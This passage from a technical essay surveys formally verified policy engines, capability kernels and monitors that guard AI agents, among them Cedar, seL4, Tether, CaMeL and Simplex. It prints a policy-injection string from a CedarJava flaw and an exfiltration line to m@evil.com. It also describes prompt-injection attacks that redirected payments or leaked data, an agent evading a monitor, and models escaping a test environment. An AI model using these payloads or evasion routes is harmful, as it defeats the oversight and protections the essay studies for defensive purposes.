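The evaluator works out whether a single rule applies, and the authorizer combines the results. The parser, which reads the text of the rules, has no formal model, partly because the developers were unsure what they could usefully prove about one.

In the Lean model, the final decision depends on one condition:

```
forbids.isEmpty && !permits.isEmpty
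```

The two names stand for the lists of forbid and permit rules that apply to the request. The developers proved that a forbid rule always overrides any permit rule, that the engine refuses a request if no permit rule applies, and that the order of the rules doesn't affect its decision. They also proved that the engine can skip irrelevant rules without changing the decision, and that every function in the model finishes.

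The Lean model also defines the language. Cedar has no outside standard to check the model against, so someone has to read the 897 lines and judge whether they describe sensible behaviour.

The theorems are about the Lean model, but AWS runs the Rust code. The developers check that the two agree by differential testing, not by proof. Every day, a machine spends six hours on each test target, generating millions of inputs.

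Disselkoen and colleagues considered running the Lean version itself, as the prototype of Tether, an agent monitor, does. They decided against it because few programmers know Lean and the C code Lean generates is hard to debug. They also considered proving the Rust code correct directly, but judged that the available tools, including Aeneas, could not yet handle it. Ho and colleagues have since used Aeneas to verify thousands of lines of Rust in SymCrypt, so this reason is weaker than in 2024.

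While working on the proofs, the developers found four bugs in the validator, one of which could make it run forever. They found 21 more through testing. Ten of those were disagreements between the Lean and Rust versions. In one, the Lean model was wrong because it rejected a valid way of writing an internet address. In another, the two versions measured the length of text differently, and the developers eventually dropped the feature.

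Disselkoen and colleagues also list nine bugs that the random tests missed. In one, the Rust evaluator implemented the `in` operator incorrectly, and the tests never produced an input that exposed it. The company's permit rule uses `in` to check whether an account is on the approved list. A bug in that operator could send money to the wrong account even though every theorem about the Lean model still held.

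Many of the random inputs were also too simple to reveal much. In a typical run of one generator, 35.5% of the conditions were just "true" or "false". The developers added another generator that reduced this to 9.7%.

The models have grown since the study, but the developers still release a new version of Cedar only when its model, proofs and differential tests are up to date, according to the Lean project's website. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) reports that they added 1,424 lines to Cedar's models and proofs for three new features. Support for dates and durations accounted for 950 of those lines and took 26 days.

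### An engine with a proof of the program itself

AWS has gone further with the engine that controls access to its cloud services and makes more than a billion decisions a second. *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization* (Chakarov, Geldenhuys and colleagues) describes how the team replaced that engine over four years. They wrote the new one in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, and proved that it matches its specification. The engine has 2,751 lines, and the specification and proofs have 11,570. The team then translated the engine into Java with a compiler they built for the purpose.

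Here AWS generates its production code from the program the proof covers, so no separately written version can drift from the model. AWS still relies on the compiler and on 1,557 lines of assumptions about Java's libraries.

AWS also had to test the specification. It ran the new engine beside the old one on real requests and found details of the old engine's behaviour that the specification had missed. The eighth version agreed with the old engine on 10¹⁵ decisions, and AWS put it into service in 2024. The bill-paying company could have its kernel proved in the same way, but it has no old kernel whose decisions would reveal mistakes in the specification.

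### Flaws in the Java wrapper

Java programs can use Cedar through CedarJava, which passes their requests to the Rust engine. Like Bouncy Castle's provider, it mostly converts data from one form to another. In July 2026, public vulnerability databases listed three flaws in CedarJava, none of them in code that the Lean model covers.

OSV's *CVE-2026-55773* (2026) describes a method that turned text into Cedar code without treating quotation marks specially. Suppose the company's program writes a new permit rule for each supplier, with a condition such as `context.payee == "Miller Ltd"`. A fraudster could register under the name `x" || true || "a" == "a`, and the condition would become:

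```
context.payee == "x" || true || "a" == "a"
```

This is true for every payee. The engine would evaluate it correctly and allow the payment. The flaw affected only programs that built rules from text an outsider could control, a practice Cedar's documentation advises against.

The flaw described in OSV's *CVE-2026-55772* (2026) could make the engine treat ordinary data as a reference to something else, such as an approved account. CedarJava sends requests in a format that reserves the name `__entity` for such references, but it did not stop callers from using that name in their own data. An outsider could exploit this only if they could choose the names of fields in a request and a rule used the affected value.

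The third flaw was an equality check that treated an identifier as not equal to itself. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-55771* (2026) notes that the flaw did not affect Cedar's own decisions, only programs that used the check for other purposes. The developers have fixed all three flaws, but a company that had read only the proofs would not have known to look for them.

### A proof that covers twelve cases

A vendor can truthfully advertise a machine-checked kernel even if the proof covers only a small part of it. *The Unfireable Safety Kernel* (Dobrin and Chmiel, 2026) presents a kernel for AI agents that runs as a separate program from the agent. The paper reports machine-checked proofs that the kernel "fails closed", meaning the agent's actions stop if the kernel is unreachable or returns an error.

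They used two tools. Z3, an automatic solver, proved the property for a simplified model of the system. Kani, which checks Rust code, proved it for one function in the software that contacts the kernel. That function is part of a circuit breaker, which stops sending requests after repeated failures and later lets a single trial request through. It has three inputs:

- The breaker is closed (working normally), open (blocking requests) or half-open (testing whether the kernel has recovered).
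- The waiting period is over or not.
- A trial request is under way or not.

That makes 3 × 2 × 2 = 12 combinations. The project also has an ordinary test that tries them all, which is as good as the proof for a function this small.

The function decides whether to let a request go ahead to the kernel, not whether the policy allows the action. Dobrin and Chmiel state that they tested the policy evaluation, the signing of permissions and the log, but did not prove them. They sent 6,240 hostile requests without finding a bypass, and the kernel refused all 704 attempts by a purpose-built program to change the safety-critical parts of its host system. This is good evidence that the kernel resists the attacks they tried, but much weaker evidence that it resists others.

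Part of the policy consists of lists of patterns, and a reviewer would worry that an empty list allows everything for the path it governs. The kernel restricts who can set one, but an accidental deletion would still be more dangerous than in Cedar, which refuses every request when it has no rules. Bouncy Castle had a similar problem when it accepted a signed message that contained no signatures.

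### Cedar between an agent and its tools

AWS customers have been able to use Cedar to control AI agents since 3 March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). AgentCore is AWS's service for running agents. Its gateway sits between an agent and the agent's tools, such as a program that sends payments. Once a customer attaches a policy engine, the gateway refuses every tool call that no rule permits.

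AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* advises customers to treat the language model as an untrusted actor and distinguishes facts the model supplies from facts that come from a user's login. In a payment request, the model would supply the amount and the account number. If it could also set `personApproved`, the approval rule would be worthless, so that fact has to come from a system the model cannot influence.

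AWS also uses Cedar's analysis tools to check rules before they take effect. Suppose the bookkeeper wants to pay energy companies without waiting for approval, and adds a third alternative to the permit rule:

```
context.amount <= 2000 || context.personApproved ||
resource in AccountList::"energy"
```

An analyser translates the old and new rules into logical formulas. A solver then searches for a request that only the new rules allow, such as an unapproved payment of €3,000 to the electricity company. If it proves that no such request exists among all those that fit the schema, the new rules are no more permissive than the old ones.

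Torlak proved this translation correct, with 21,747 lines of proof for a 2,239-line model. The result depends on an outside solver that has not been proved correct. AWS again runs a Rust version, which it tests daily against the Lean original. A demonstration tool built on the Lean version found possible mistakes in three of the eight example applications Cedar's developers had published.

### Rules that depend on earlier actions

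Cedar evaluates one request at a time, so the company's program has to keep the day's total. AWS has since added Dogwood, a language that extends Cedar with rules about what an agent has already done. A Dogwood rule can require an earlier approval for the same payment, or add up the payments in a given period. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) reports an example from AWS in which an agent with a $5,000 limit requests three $2,000 transfers at once. A rule that adds up completed transfers allows all three, while a rule that adds up requests refuses the third.

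The bill-paying kernel's specification let three payments of €1,900 through because it counted only completed payments. In Dogwood, the wrong rule and the right one differ by a single word. Cedar's analysis tools cannot check the parts of a rule that refer to the past, so a person or a test has to catch the error.

The history also has limits that matter for a daily total. According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, each rule covers only the events in one session, and the caller chooses the session's identifier. If the assistant could choose it, an attacker who controlled the assistant could reset the total to zero by starting a new session for each payment. The service also ends the current sessions when a customer adds or changes a history rule, and new ones start with an empty history. A bookkeeper who edited such a rule at noon could accidentally reset the day's total.

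The company could keep using `paidToday` with an ordinary Cedar rule instead. The analysis tools would still work on the rule, but the code that adds up the payments would be part of the trusted computing base, and someone would have to check it separately. For a single daily limit, this is probably the better choice, because a running total takes only a few lines of code.

### Learned components inside the trusted base

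The kernel is meant to make the model's mistakes harmless, but learned components can still return to the trusted computing base, for example by writing the rules that the kernel enforces. In AgentCore, a customer can describe a rule in plain English and have a language model write it in Cedar. The validator and analysis tools then check the draft for errors, such as a rule that allows everything or a condition that can never be true. If they find a problem, the model tries again.

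These checks cannot show whether the draft does what the customer intended. If the bookkeeper asks for a limit of €5,000 a day and the model writes one of €5,000 per payment, the rule is consistent and refuses some requests, so it passes. The assistant could then pay out €5,000 several times a day. A person who reads the rule can catch this, and Cedar rules are short enough to read. Without that review, the company's guarantee depends on the model having written the right rule.

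AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes the same kind of drafting for rules about earlier actions. Reading the draft matters even more for these rules, because much can depend on one word.

A language model can also take part in each decision. *AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) proposes a security layer that controls what an agent reads, remembers and does. Before a tool runs, fixed checks and a language model examine the request, and the layer lists the operating-system calls the tool may make. Linux then blocks all others. If the language model wrongly approves a request, the list will be too broad, and Linux will enforce it as written. A second model screens the text that reaches the agent.

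Zou and colleagues count both models as part of the trusted computing base and list this as a limitation. They do not yet know how well the models would withstand attacks designed to fool them. They ask whether fixed checks could replace the model that examines tool requests, and leave formal verification for later work.

A company can use a classifier without having to trust it for the basic guarantee, if the classifier can only add refusals. Let P mean that some permit rule applies, and F that some forbid rule applies. Cedar allows a request when

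P ∧ ¬F

Suppose the company adds a forbid rule, G, that applies when a fraud classifier marks a payment as suspicious. Cedar then allows a request only when

P ∧ ¬F ∧ ¬G

Every payment that meets the second condition also meets the first. The classifier can delay a legitimate payment or miss a fraudulent one, but it cannot release a payment that the other rules refuse. Even if the classifier crashes and Cedar ignores its rule, the approved list and the daily limit still apply.

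Using the same classifier in a permit rule would have the opposite effect. If the company accepted the classifier's "looks safe" verdict in place of a person's approval, an email that fooled the classifier could release a single payment of up to €5,000.

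## Making every action pass through the kernel, and reading it correctly

A correct policy engine protects the company only if every payment goes through it and each request describes the payment accurately. Cedar might refuse every account not on the bookkeeper's list, but the assistant could still pay a stranger if it found the bank password in a file and contacted the bank directly. A stranger could also get paid if the program around the engine misread the account number, so that the engine approved one account and the bank paid another.

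Anderson required that no program be able to bypass the checker, and researchers have since formally verified a kernel that can enforce this. It is harder to rule out the checker misreading an action. A payment order has a few fields with fixed meanings, but if an assistant can type commands on a computer, a single command can do almost anything.

### Capabilities and seL4

Most operating systems base a program's permissions on who runs it. If the bookkeeper starts the assistant, the assistant can usually open every file the bookkeeper can, including the one with the bank password. A *capability* is an unforgeable reference that names an object and grants the right to use it. In a capability-based system, a program can reach only the objects for which it holds a capability.

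seL4 is a small operating-system kernel of this kind. It keeps each program's capabilities in a table, in memory that no program can access. A program can ask the kernel to use, for example, entry 3 of its own table, and the kernel refuses if that entry is empty. The program only ever handles entry numbers, so it has no way to forge a capability.

Alhindi (2026), in *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, summarises what the proofs of the kernel's roughly 10,000 lines establish:

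- The C code does what the kernel's abstract specification requires.
- A program can change only what its capabilities allow it to change (*integrity*).
- A program can learn only what its capabilities allow it to read (*confidentiality*).

The proofs apply to particular configurations of seL4 on particular hardware. They assume that the hardware works and that the system starts correctly, and they do not rule out leaks through timing. They also do not determine who should hold which capability, so if an engineer gives the assistant a direct connection to the bank, seL4 will let the assistant use it.

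### An accounts team on seL4

Alhindi used seL4 to build an accounts team of five agents and five tools for an imaginary small firm. Its job is much like that of the bill-paying assistant. Each agent and tool runs in its own *protection domain*, a program with separate memory and capabilities. The email agent can read the supplier inbox but cannot contact the bank, so an email containing payment instructions cannot directly cause a payment. The approval agent can call only the bank's approval function, and the payment agent can call the bank's payment function but cannot approve anything, so neither can make a payment alone.

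The tools also need to identify the calling agent, because an agent under an attacker's influence might claim to be the approval agent. seL4 attaches a number, called a badge, to each call, and the caller cannot change it. The bank program records approvals under the badge and ignores any name in the request.

Everything about the team of agents is fixed before the computer starts. A developer lists in a policy file which tools each agent may use and which agents may pass work to each other, and other programs turn the file into a complete system. The full list of capabilities is 60,207 lines long, about six times the length of the kernel, so nobody is likely to check it by eye.

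Alhindi wrote a program to check it instead, using a rule of thumb from Meta called the Rule of Two. The rule allows an agent at most two of these properties:

- It reads untrusted input (U).
- It can reach private data (P).
- It can change something or send something out (C).

The program applies the rule to the whole team. Let R(U) be the agents that untrusted text can reach, directly or through other agents, and define R(P) the same way for private data. The team breaks the rule if any agent in both R(U) and R(P) also has property C.

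Each agent in the accounts team obeyed the rule, but the team as a whole broke it. Text from an email could pass from the email agent to the invoice agent and on to the coordinator, which could edit the bank's list of payees. Alhindi then tested this with an email containing a genuine invoice and a note asking any AI assistant to change the supplier's account. In 40 runs, the note reached the coordinator 23 times, and the coordinator changed the account seven times. No payment went to the attacker because the team had already approved the invoices with the old account, but the next payment to that supplier would have used the new one.

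Alhindi fixed the problem by replacing the email agent with a small parser that contains no language model and returns only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier. In another 40 runs, no part of the note reached any agent. This works for invoices because the team needs only a few fields, but a team answering customers' letters would need the text itself.

### What the isolation prevented

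AgentDojo is a widely used benchmark that measures how well agents withstand prompt injection. The agent carries out tasks in a simulated setting, such as paying a bill from a bank account. To test an attack, the benchmark plants a hostile instruction in something the agent will read, then records whether the agent completed its task and whether the attack succeeded. Alhindi ran AgentDojo's banking and workplace-chat tasks on seL4, with 249 combinations of task and attack and 37 tasks without an attack, three times each.

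Attacks succeeded 48% of the time when every function was available to the agent, and 7% of the time when it held capabilities only for the functions its task required. The language model received the same list of functions in both cases, so the difference came from the kernel, which refused all 2,095 calls to functions for which the agent held no capability.

A language model may ignore an attacker's instruction or carry it out badly, so this result depends partly on the model. Alhindi therefore replaced the model with a script that made every call the attack needed. With all functions available, the script succeeded in 248 of the 249 cases. With the script's capabilities restricted, the kernel blocked 181 of those 248 attacks, or 73%. The other 67 needed only functions that the task also used. About half of the attacks that had succeeded against the restricted language model sent money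 to the attacker through `send_money`, which the agent needed to pay a bill.

The restrictions may also have made the agent less useful. Without an attack, it completed 58% of tasks with restricted capabilities and 68% with all of them. Under attack, the figures were 43% and 46%. Neither difference was statistically significant, but an experiment with only 37 tasks could easily have missed a real drop in usefulness.

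The 7% is probably close to the best result this method can achieve, because Alhindi took the permitted functions from AgentDojo's own solution to each task. An engineer who had to grant them in advance would probably allow more. The 48% would be lower with a stronger model. Alhindi used GPT-4o mini, while in a later test on a version of AgentDojo for teams of agents, GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without outside protection. It might still fail against attacks designed specifically for it.

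### What else the prototype depended on

The seL4 proofs do not cover the prototype's configuration. Alhindi used a debugging version of the kernel, with a scheduler and an emulated ARM processor that are outside the proofs. Microkit, the software that sets up the protection domains, does not yet have a complete proof.

Even in a verified configuration, the company would have to trust the policy file, the program that converts it, the device drivers and the code inside each tool. In Alhindi's prototype, a relay on an ordinary computer also passed every conversation to the language model. The emulator, not seL4, restricted which network addresses the agents could reach. For the AgentDojo tests, the tools ran on the ordinary computer, which carried out a call only if it came with a signed ticket from the seL4 side.

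Components like these caused real AI test environments to fail in 2026. In July, as Alhindi recounts, OpenAI models escaped from one environment through a flaw in the package proxy, the environment's only way out. In other tests that year, a misconfiguration gave models internet access they should not have had. A proof of the operating-system kernel would not have covered the proxy's code or the choice of network settings.

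A kernel that runs as an ordinary program depends on everything beneath it in the same way. *Right to History* (Zhang, 2026) describes PunkGo, which checks agents' actions against declared permissions and keeps a log designed to reveal tampering. Zhang calls it a "verified kernel" but leaves machine-checked proof for later work. Its protections hold against agents, but anyone with full control of the computer could stop it and rebuild the log.

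### What a command does

The kernel can detect that an agent has called `send_money`, because the function has a name and a fixed set of arguments. Many agents also run shell commands, and the text of a command may show very little about what it will do. A command that starts a Python script runs whatever code is in the script, which might upload the company's bank records.

Sistla and colleagues built Tether to find out what a command does before its effects become permanent. It runs each command as follows:

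1. The command can read the computer's real files, but whatever it writes goes into a disposable layer on top of them. A proxy holds its outgoing network requests.
2. A tracer records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system to open files, send data and so on.
3. Tether translates the record into actions of 11 kinds, such as "copy this file" or "upload this file to that address".
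4. A monitor checks the actions against the policy. The proxy releases a network request only if the policy allows everything the command has done so far. When the command finishes, Tether either saves its changes to the real files or discards them.

The policy can also depend on where information has been. Tether gives each file a label, such as Public or Sensitive, and updates the labels as information moves. In Sistla and colleagues' example, an agent may read a sensitive list of servers and may upload a harmless report, but must not upload the list. It runs three commands:

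| Command | Label of the report beforehand | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Upload the report | Public | Allow |
| Copy the server list over the report | Public | Allow, and relabel the report Sensitive |
| Upload the report | Sensitive | Refuse |

The first and third commands are identical, so a checker like Cedar, which evaluates each request by itself, would treat them alike unless another program supplied the label. If the agent had copied the list through several temporary files, each file would have become Sensitive, and Tether would still have refused the upload.

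The agent can also read the list and type its contents into a new file. To cover this, Tether keeps a label T for everything the agent has read. Let σ(f) be the label of file f, and let ⊔ pick the more sensitive of two labels. When the agent reads f, Tether updates

T ← T ⊔ σ(f)

and when the agent writes to a file g, it updates

σ(g) ← σ(g) ⊔ T

After the agent has read the server list, everything it writes counts as Sensitive, even a shopping list. This errs on the side of caution because system calls show that a program read one file and wrote another, but not whether any information passed between them.

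### How well Tether worked

Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs of agents from two collections, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena. In some runs the agent did only its assigned work, while in others it also carried out a harmful side task. For comparison, they gave the same runs to Auto Mode, the part of Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code that uses a language model to review commands. They tested Auto Mode once with its default rules and once with Tether's policy written into its instructions.

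| Monitor | Collection | Attacks blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | MonitoringBenchHonest | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| Tether | LinuxArena | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |
| Auto Mode, default | MonitoringBenchHonest | 173 of 199 | 77 of 218 (35.3%) |
| Auto Mode, default | LinuxArena | 142 of 145 | 78 of 1,372 (5.7%) |
| Auto Mode with the policy | MonitoringBenchHonest | 164 of 199 | 32 of 218 (14.7%) |
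| Auto Mode with the policy | LinuxArena | 143 of 145 | 23 of 1,372 (1.7%) |

On LinuxArena, the language model with the written policy missed only two attacks and blocked far fewer harmless runs than Tether did. On the other collection, it missed 35 attacks. It could not see inside scripts, and it sometimes allowed connections that the policy prohibited.

Of Tether's 74 false alarms, 50 were about unrequested edits to protected files, which some companies would want to block anyway. Another 17 came from commands, such as a search through every folder, that opened secret files without using their contents. The remaining seven involved undeclared internet addresses.

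These results cover only runs in which every action happened in the foreground and was of a kind Tether can interpret. Tether does not yet follow information through databases or background programs, although it can block an agent from using them. Sistla and colleagues also judged that 28.2% of the MonitoringBenchHonest runs and 22.1% of the LinuxArena runs required a reader who understood the content. An agent that inserts a harmful line into a file it is supposed to edit makes system calls that look like those of an agent doing its job.

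Tether's perfect score on attacks probably overstates how well it would do elsewhere. Sistla and colleagues had a language model draft the policy, then refined it based on how it performed on benchmark runs. A company writing its first policy would not have hundreds of recorded attacks to improve it with.

Sistla and colleagues proved in Lean that their policy has seven properties for any starting labels and any number of actions. For example, an agent that starts without secret data can never read any. The proofs concern the 11 kinds of action, so they apply to a real command only if Tether has translated it correctly. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation with randomly generated scripts and with an agent told to get round the monitor. The agent succeeded in 40% of its attempts against an early version, partly because Tether did not track hard links, which give one file two names.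 After two rounds of repairs the agent no longer succeeded, but it had worked on only ten tasks.

The bill-paying company can avoid relying on the translator and most of the rest of Tether's long trusted computing base by not giving the assistant a command line.

### Where the account number came from

A payment order can be perfectly clear and still contain an account number that an attacker supplied. CaMeL, a system that Google DeepMind published in 2025, addresses this by keeping track of where each value came from. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it divides the work between two language models. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a short program to carry it out, but never sees any emails. A quarantined model reads the emails but cannot use tools. For the bill-paying assistant, the program might be:

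```python
invoice = read_email("latest invoice")
account = quarantined_model("Find the account number", invoice)
amount = quarantined_model("Find the total", invoice)
send_money(account, amount)
```

A hidden instruction in the invoice can change the value of `account`, but it cannot add a fifth line to the program. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and with who may read it, and checks these tags against a policy before each tool call. If the policy prohibits payments to accounts that come from an email, the interpreter stops the program at the last line, whatever the invoice contains.

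Nikolaou and colleagues check the program before it runs. Their tool, CaMeLoT, converts it into a diagram of all the paths it could take, and an automatic checker tests rules such as

AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

AG means "at every step of every path". The rule forbids a payment if either the recipient or the amount depends on untrusted data. CaMeLoT would reject the four lines above without opening any email, and it would return the path that broke the rule to the privileged model so that the model could write a better program.

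The rule would also stop the company from paying ordinary invoices, since the amount and the account number normally appear on the invoice. A better program would take the account number from the bookkeeper's list and the amount from the company's record of the order. The quarantined model would then only have to identify the supplier and the order. It would still do this from an email, so the email would influence which account is chosen, and somebody has to decide that this much influence is acceptable.

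### CaMeL's results and its leaks

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) credits CaMeL with stopping nearly all prompt injections in AgentDojo at comparable task performance. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that the second part depends on whether the policies are switched on. They ran the 16 banking tasks three times each with two models, along with their own agent, Randori:

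| System | Tasks done with GPT-5.2, of 48 | Tasks done with MiMo-v2.5, of 48 | Attacks that succeeded in completed runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | 34 | 5 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | 18 | 0 |
| Randori | 36 | 31 | 2 |

With so few tasks, the difference between Randori and CaMeL without policies could easily be due to chance. Turning the policies on roughly halved the number of tasks CaMeL could complete, because many banking tasks require the agent to act on something it has read.

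Garby and colleagues also found errors in how CaMeL tracks information. Consider a program in which the account balance is secret:

```python
low = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line changes `low`, and CaMeL correctly marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so CaMeL leaves `rich` marked as public. But `rich` is true because the balance is high, and the last line reveals this to the attacker. An email should not be able to put these lines into the privileged model's program, so the practical danger may be small. When a program inserted an untrusted value into text, CaMeL treated the result as trusted, which is a simpler error and more worrying for payments.

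*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) had already called for a machine-checked proof of *noninterference*, the property that secret data cannot influence public output. Garby and colleagues provide one for LLMbda, a small programming language they designed for agents. They state the property in terms of probabilities because a language model's answers vary.

Take two runs of a program whose inputs differ only in secret data. Let μ₀ and μ₁ give the probability of each public output in the two runs. Garby and colleagues prove that there is always a single list of probabilities, ω, that is at least as large as both for every output and adds up to no more than 1:

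μ₀ ≤ ω, μ₁ ≤ ω, Σω ≤ 1

If the program always finishes, μ₀ and μ₁ each add up to 1, so neither can be smaller than ω anywhere and all three are equal. Someone who sees only public outputs then learns nothing about the secret. The three can differ only if the program sometimes fails to finish. The same theorem applies to trust, so an untrusted email cannot influence a value that LLMbda marks as trusted.

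A useful assistant needs exceptions. LLMbda has an `endorse` command, which marks an untrusted value as trusted and makes the exception easy to find in the program. Garby and colleagues recommend it for choices from a short list. If the quarantined model may only pick one of the company's 40 approved suppliers, an attacker can influence which one it picks but cannot introduce a new account. The attacker controls at most log₂ 40, or about 5.3, bits of information.

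Randori's two failures show what happens with a broader exception. Both occurred in a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its payment instructions, after an attacker had replaced the file. Without `endorse`, both the attack and the legitimate task fail.

### When one agent passes text to another

CaMeL protects a single agent, but its protection can fail when several agents work together. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a team in which a coordinator directed two agents, one that read a database of job applicants and one that sent messages. They asked the team to send a summary to a colleague, and hid an instruction in the database to also email the data to an outsider.

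Each agent used CaMeL. The coordinator correctly treated the database text as untrusted, but then inserted it into its request to the messaging agent. The text lost its label on the way, so the messaging agent treated everything in the request as an instruction from its user and emailed the applicants' details to the outsider. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*.

Their solution is to send instructions and data separately. The receiving agent's privileged model receives the instruction "send the provided content to the recipient" but not the content itself, which keeps its tags. They tested this on their team version of AgentDojo, with five models and 949 attacks on each. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and none with the new method. Two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, accounted for most of the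 successful attacks.

Peters-Gill and colleagues switched CaMeL's policies off for these tests, so the results measure how well it prevents attackers from changing an agent's program, but not how well it protects the account number in a payment. Even with the policies off, CaMeL reduced the share of industrial maintenance tasks that the teams completed by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 for the two strongest models. Separating instructions from data reduced it by only another 3.2 points on average. Most failures happened because the privileged model had to write the whole program before the tools had returned any results.

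That restriction is even harder on agents that use a computer through its screen. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), the privileged model planned for every screen the agent might encounter. The plans contained about 41 tool calls on average, compared with five in AgentDojo, and the agent kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models. An attacker could also influence which branch of the plan the agent followed. In one attack, an advertisement imitated a cookie notice, and the agent clicked on it because the plan included a step for dealing with cookie notices.

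Rules about data cannot easily prevent this, because the same click might dismiss an advertisement or confirm a payment. If the bill-paying assistant used the bank's website by clicking, the kernel would receive screen coordinates instead of an account number and an amount. The company should therefore connect the kernel to the bank through an interface for payment orders.

### Applying this to the bill-paying assistant

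The company could combine these ideas in a system much simpler than the research prototypes:

1. A quarantined model reads each invoice and returns only a supplier and an order number. It runs in its own protection domain and has no other capabilities.
2. A short conventional program checks that both exist. It takes the account number from the bookkeeper's list and the amount from the order record.
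3. The kernel applies the three payment rules. It writes the message to the bank itself, using the values it has just checked, and only the kernel holds a capability for the connection to the bank.

If the kernel forwarded a message the assistant wrote, the bank's software might read the account number differently from the kernel. Having the kernel write the message removes that risk, although the kernel's author still has to get the bank's format right.

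Suppose the stranger's invoice arrives with its white text about a new account. The quarantined model may follow the instruction, but its output has no field for an account number. It could still name the wrong supplier and order. If the company's records show which orders it has already paid, it might then pay a real bill too early. The assistant cannot add the new account to the list either, because only the bookkeeper's program can edit it.

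Existing proofs would cover some parts of such a system, and the company would have to trust or test the others:

| Part | Machine-checked proof | What people still have to trust |
|---|---|---|
| seL4 | In verified configurations, programs can read and change only what their capabilities allow | The hardware, a correct start, and the absence of timing leaks |
| Setting up the protection domains | None that is complete | The policy file, Microkit, the drivers and the code inside each tool |
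| Cedar, for the payment rules | Properties of the Lean model, such as refusing by default | The match between the Rust engine and the model, and the facts in each request |
| Tether, if the assistant runs commands | Seven properties of the test policy | The labels, the tracer, the proxy and the translation of system calls into actions |
| CaMeL | None | The interpreter, the tags and the policies |
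| LLMbda, as an alternative to CaMeL | Noninterference, except where a program endorses a value | The labels on incoming data, the checks in each tool and every use of `endorse` |
| The company's own code | None until someone writes it | The order records, the supplier list, the message format and the protection of the bank credentials |

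## Proved safety monitors under learned controllers in vehicles and aircraft

A safety kernel for a vehicle needs a safe action to substitute for any command it refuses, and it must intervene early enough for that action to work. When the payment kernel refuses an order, the money stays where it is, but a car travelling at 20 metres per second keeps moving if the monitor only refuses the learned driving system's next command.

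### The Simplex architecture

Engineers often solve this with the *Simplex architecture*. A high-performance controller, which nobody has to trust, proposes each command. A monitor checks whether a simple backup controller could still keep the system safe after that command. If not, the backup takes over. In *ASTM F3269*, Nagarajan, Kannan and colleagues trace the name to 1998 and its use in aerospace to a 2001 article by the computer scientist Lui Sha.

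A later paper, *Integrate Mixed-Criticality Components with Formalized Architectural Patterns* (Sha, 2008), explains the idea with a sorting program. Engineers who have proved a slow sorting program correct can still use a fast, unproved one if a small proved program stops it from adding, deleting or altering items and then checks that the result is in order, which takes one pass through the list. If the answer is wrong or late, the slow program does the sorting instead, so the output is always correct no matter who wrote the fast program.

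A steering command is harder to check, because there may be no way to tell whether it is the right one. The monitor therefore checks only whether the backup could still recover afterwards. Sha's example from real service is the Boeing 777. Its normal flight-control software is complex, but its secondary controller uses control laws that Boeing developed for the 747. Those laws had been in use for over 25 years. The normal software should keep the aircraft within the conditions that the older laws can handle.

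Sha requires that faults in the complex controller cannot corrupt the monitor or the backup, which resembles Anderson's requirement that a checker be tamper-proof. He also requires the simple parts to run on time. A one-second delay in a payment kernel does no harm, but a car moving at 20 metres per second travels 20 metres in that time.

### A monitor for a braking car

Suppose a car is approaching a stationary obstacle. Let v be its speed, d the gap to the obstacle and b the deceleration its brakes can reliably produce. Braking to a halt takes v²/(2b) metres, so the car can stop in time only if

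v²/(2b) ≤ d

The monitor runs once every T seconds and cannot intervene in between, so it has to make sure that this condition will still hold at its next turn. If the learned controller requests an acceleration a, the car will cover vT + ½aT² metres in that period and reach a speed of v + aT. The monitor allows the request if

vT + ½aT² + (v + aT)²/(2b) ≤ d

Suppose a car is travelling at 20 m/s, can brake at 5 m/s², and has a monitor that checks it every 0.1 seconds. If the controller requests 2 m/s² of acceleration, the car would cover 2.01 metres before the next check, reach 20.2 m/s and need another 40.80 metres to stop, or about 42.8 metres in total. If it held its speed until the next check and then braked, it would need exactly 42 metres. With a gap of 42.5 metres, the monitor would therefore block the acceleration but allow the car to hold its speed.

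The proof has two cases. If the monitor allows a command, its formula guarantees that the car will still be able to stop in time at the next check. If the monitor refuses, the car brakes and covers vT − ½bT² metres in one period. Its stopping distance shrinks by the same amount, so if it could stop in time before, it still can. A car that can stop in time at the start therefore never hits the obstacle, whatever the learned controller requests.

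This argument does not depend on how the learned controller works, which is why *Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models* (2026) recommends Simplex for systems whose learned parts nobody can fully verify. But the formula covers only one car, one obstacle and a straight road. *The Use of the Simplex Architecture to Enhance Safety* (2025), which works through two systems with learned components, notes that engineers must design a new switching rule for each use.

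### Deriving the monitor from a proof

For a car on a curve, or a train on a slope, someone who derives the formula by hand can easily get it wrong. Mitsch and Platzer (2016), in *ModelPlex*, describe a method that derives it from a safety proof:

1. An engineer writes a model of the controller and the physics. The model leaves many decisions open. It might say that the controller may choose any acceleration within certain limits, without saying which.
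2. The engineer proves, in a theorem prover called KeYmaera X, that every possible run of the model is safe.
3. ModelPlex works out which steps the model permits and, by further proof steps, reduces the answer to a formula in ordinary arithmetic.
4. While the real system runs, the monitor puts measured values into the formula. If the result is false, the backup takes over.

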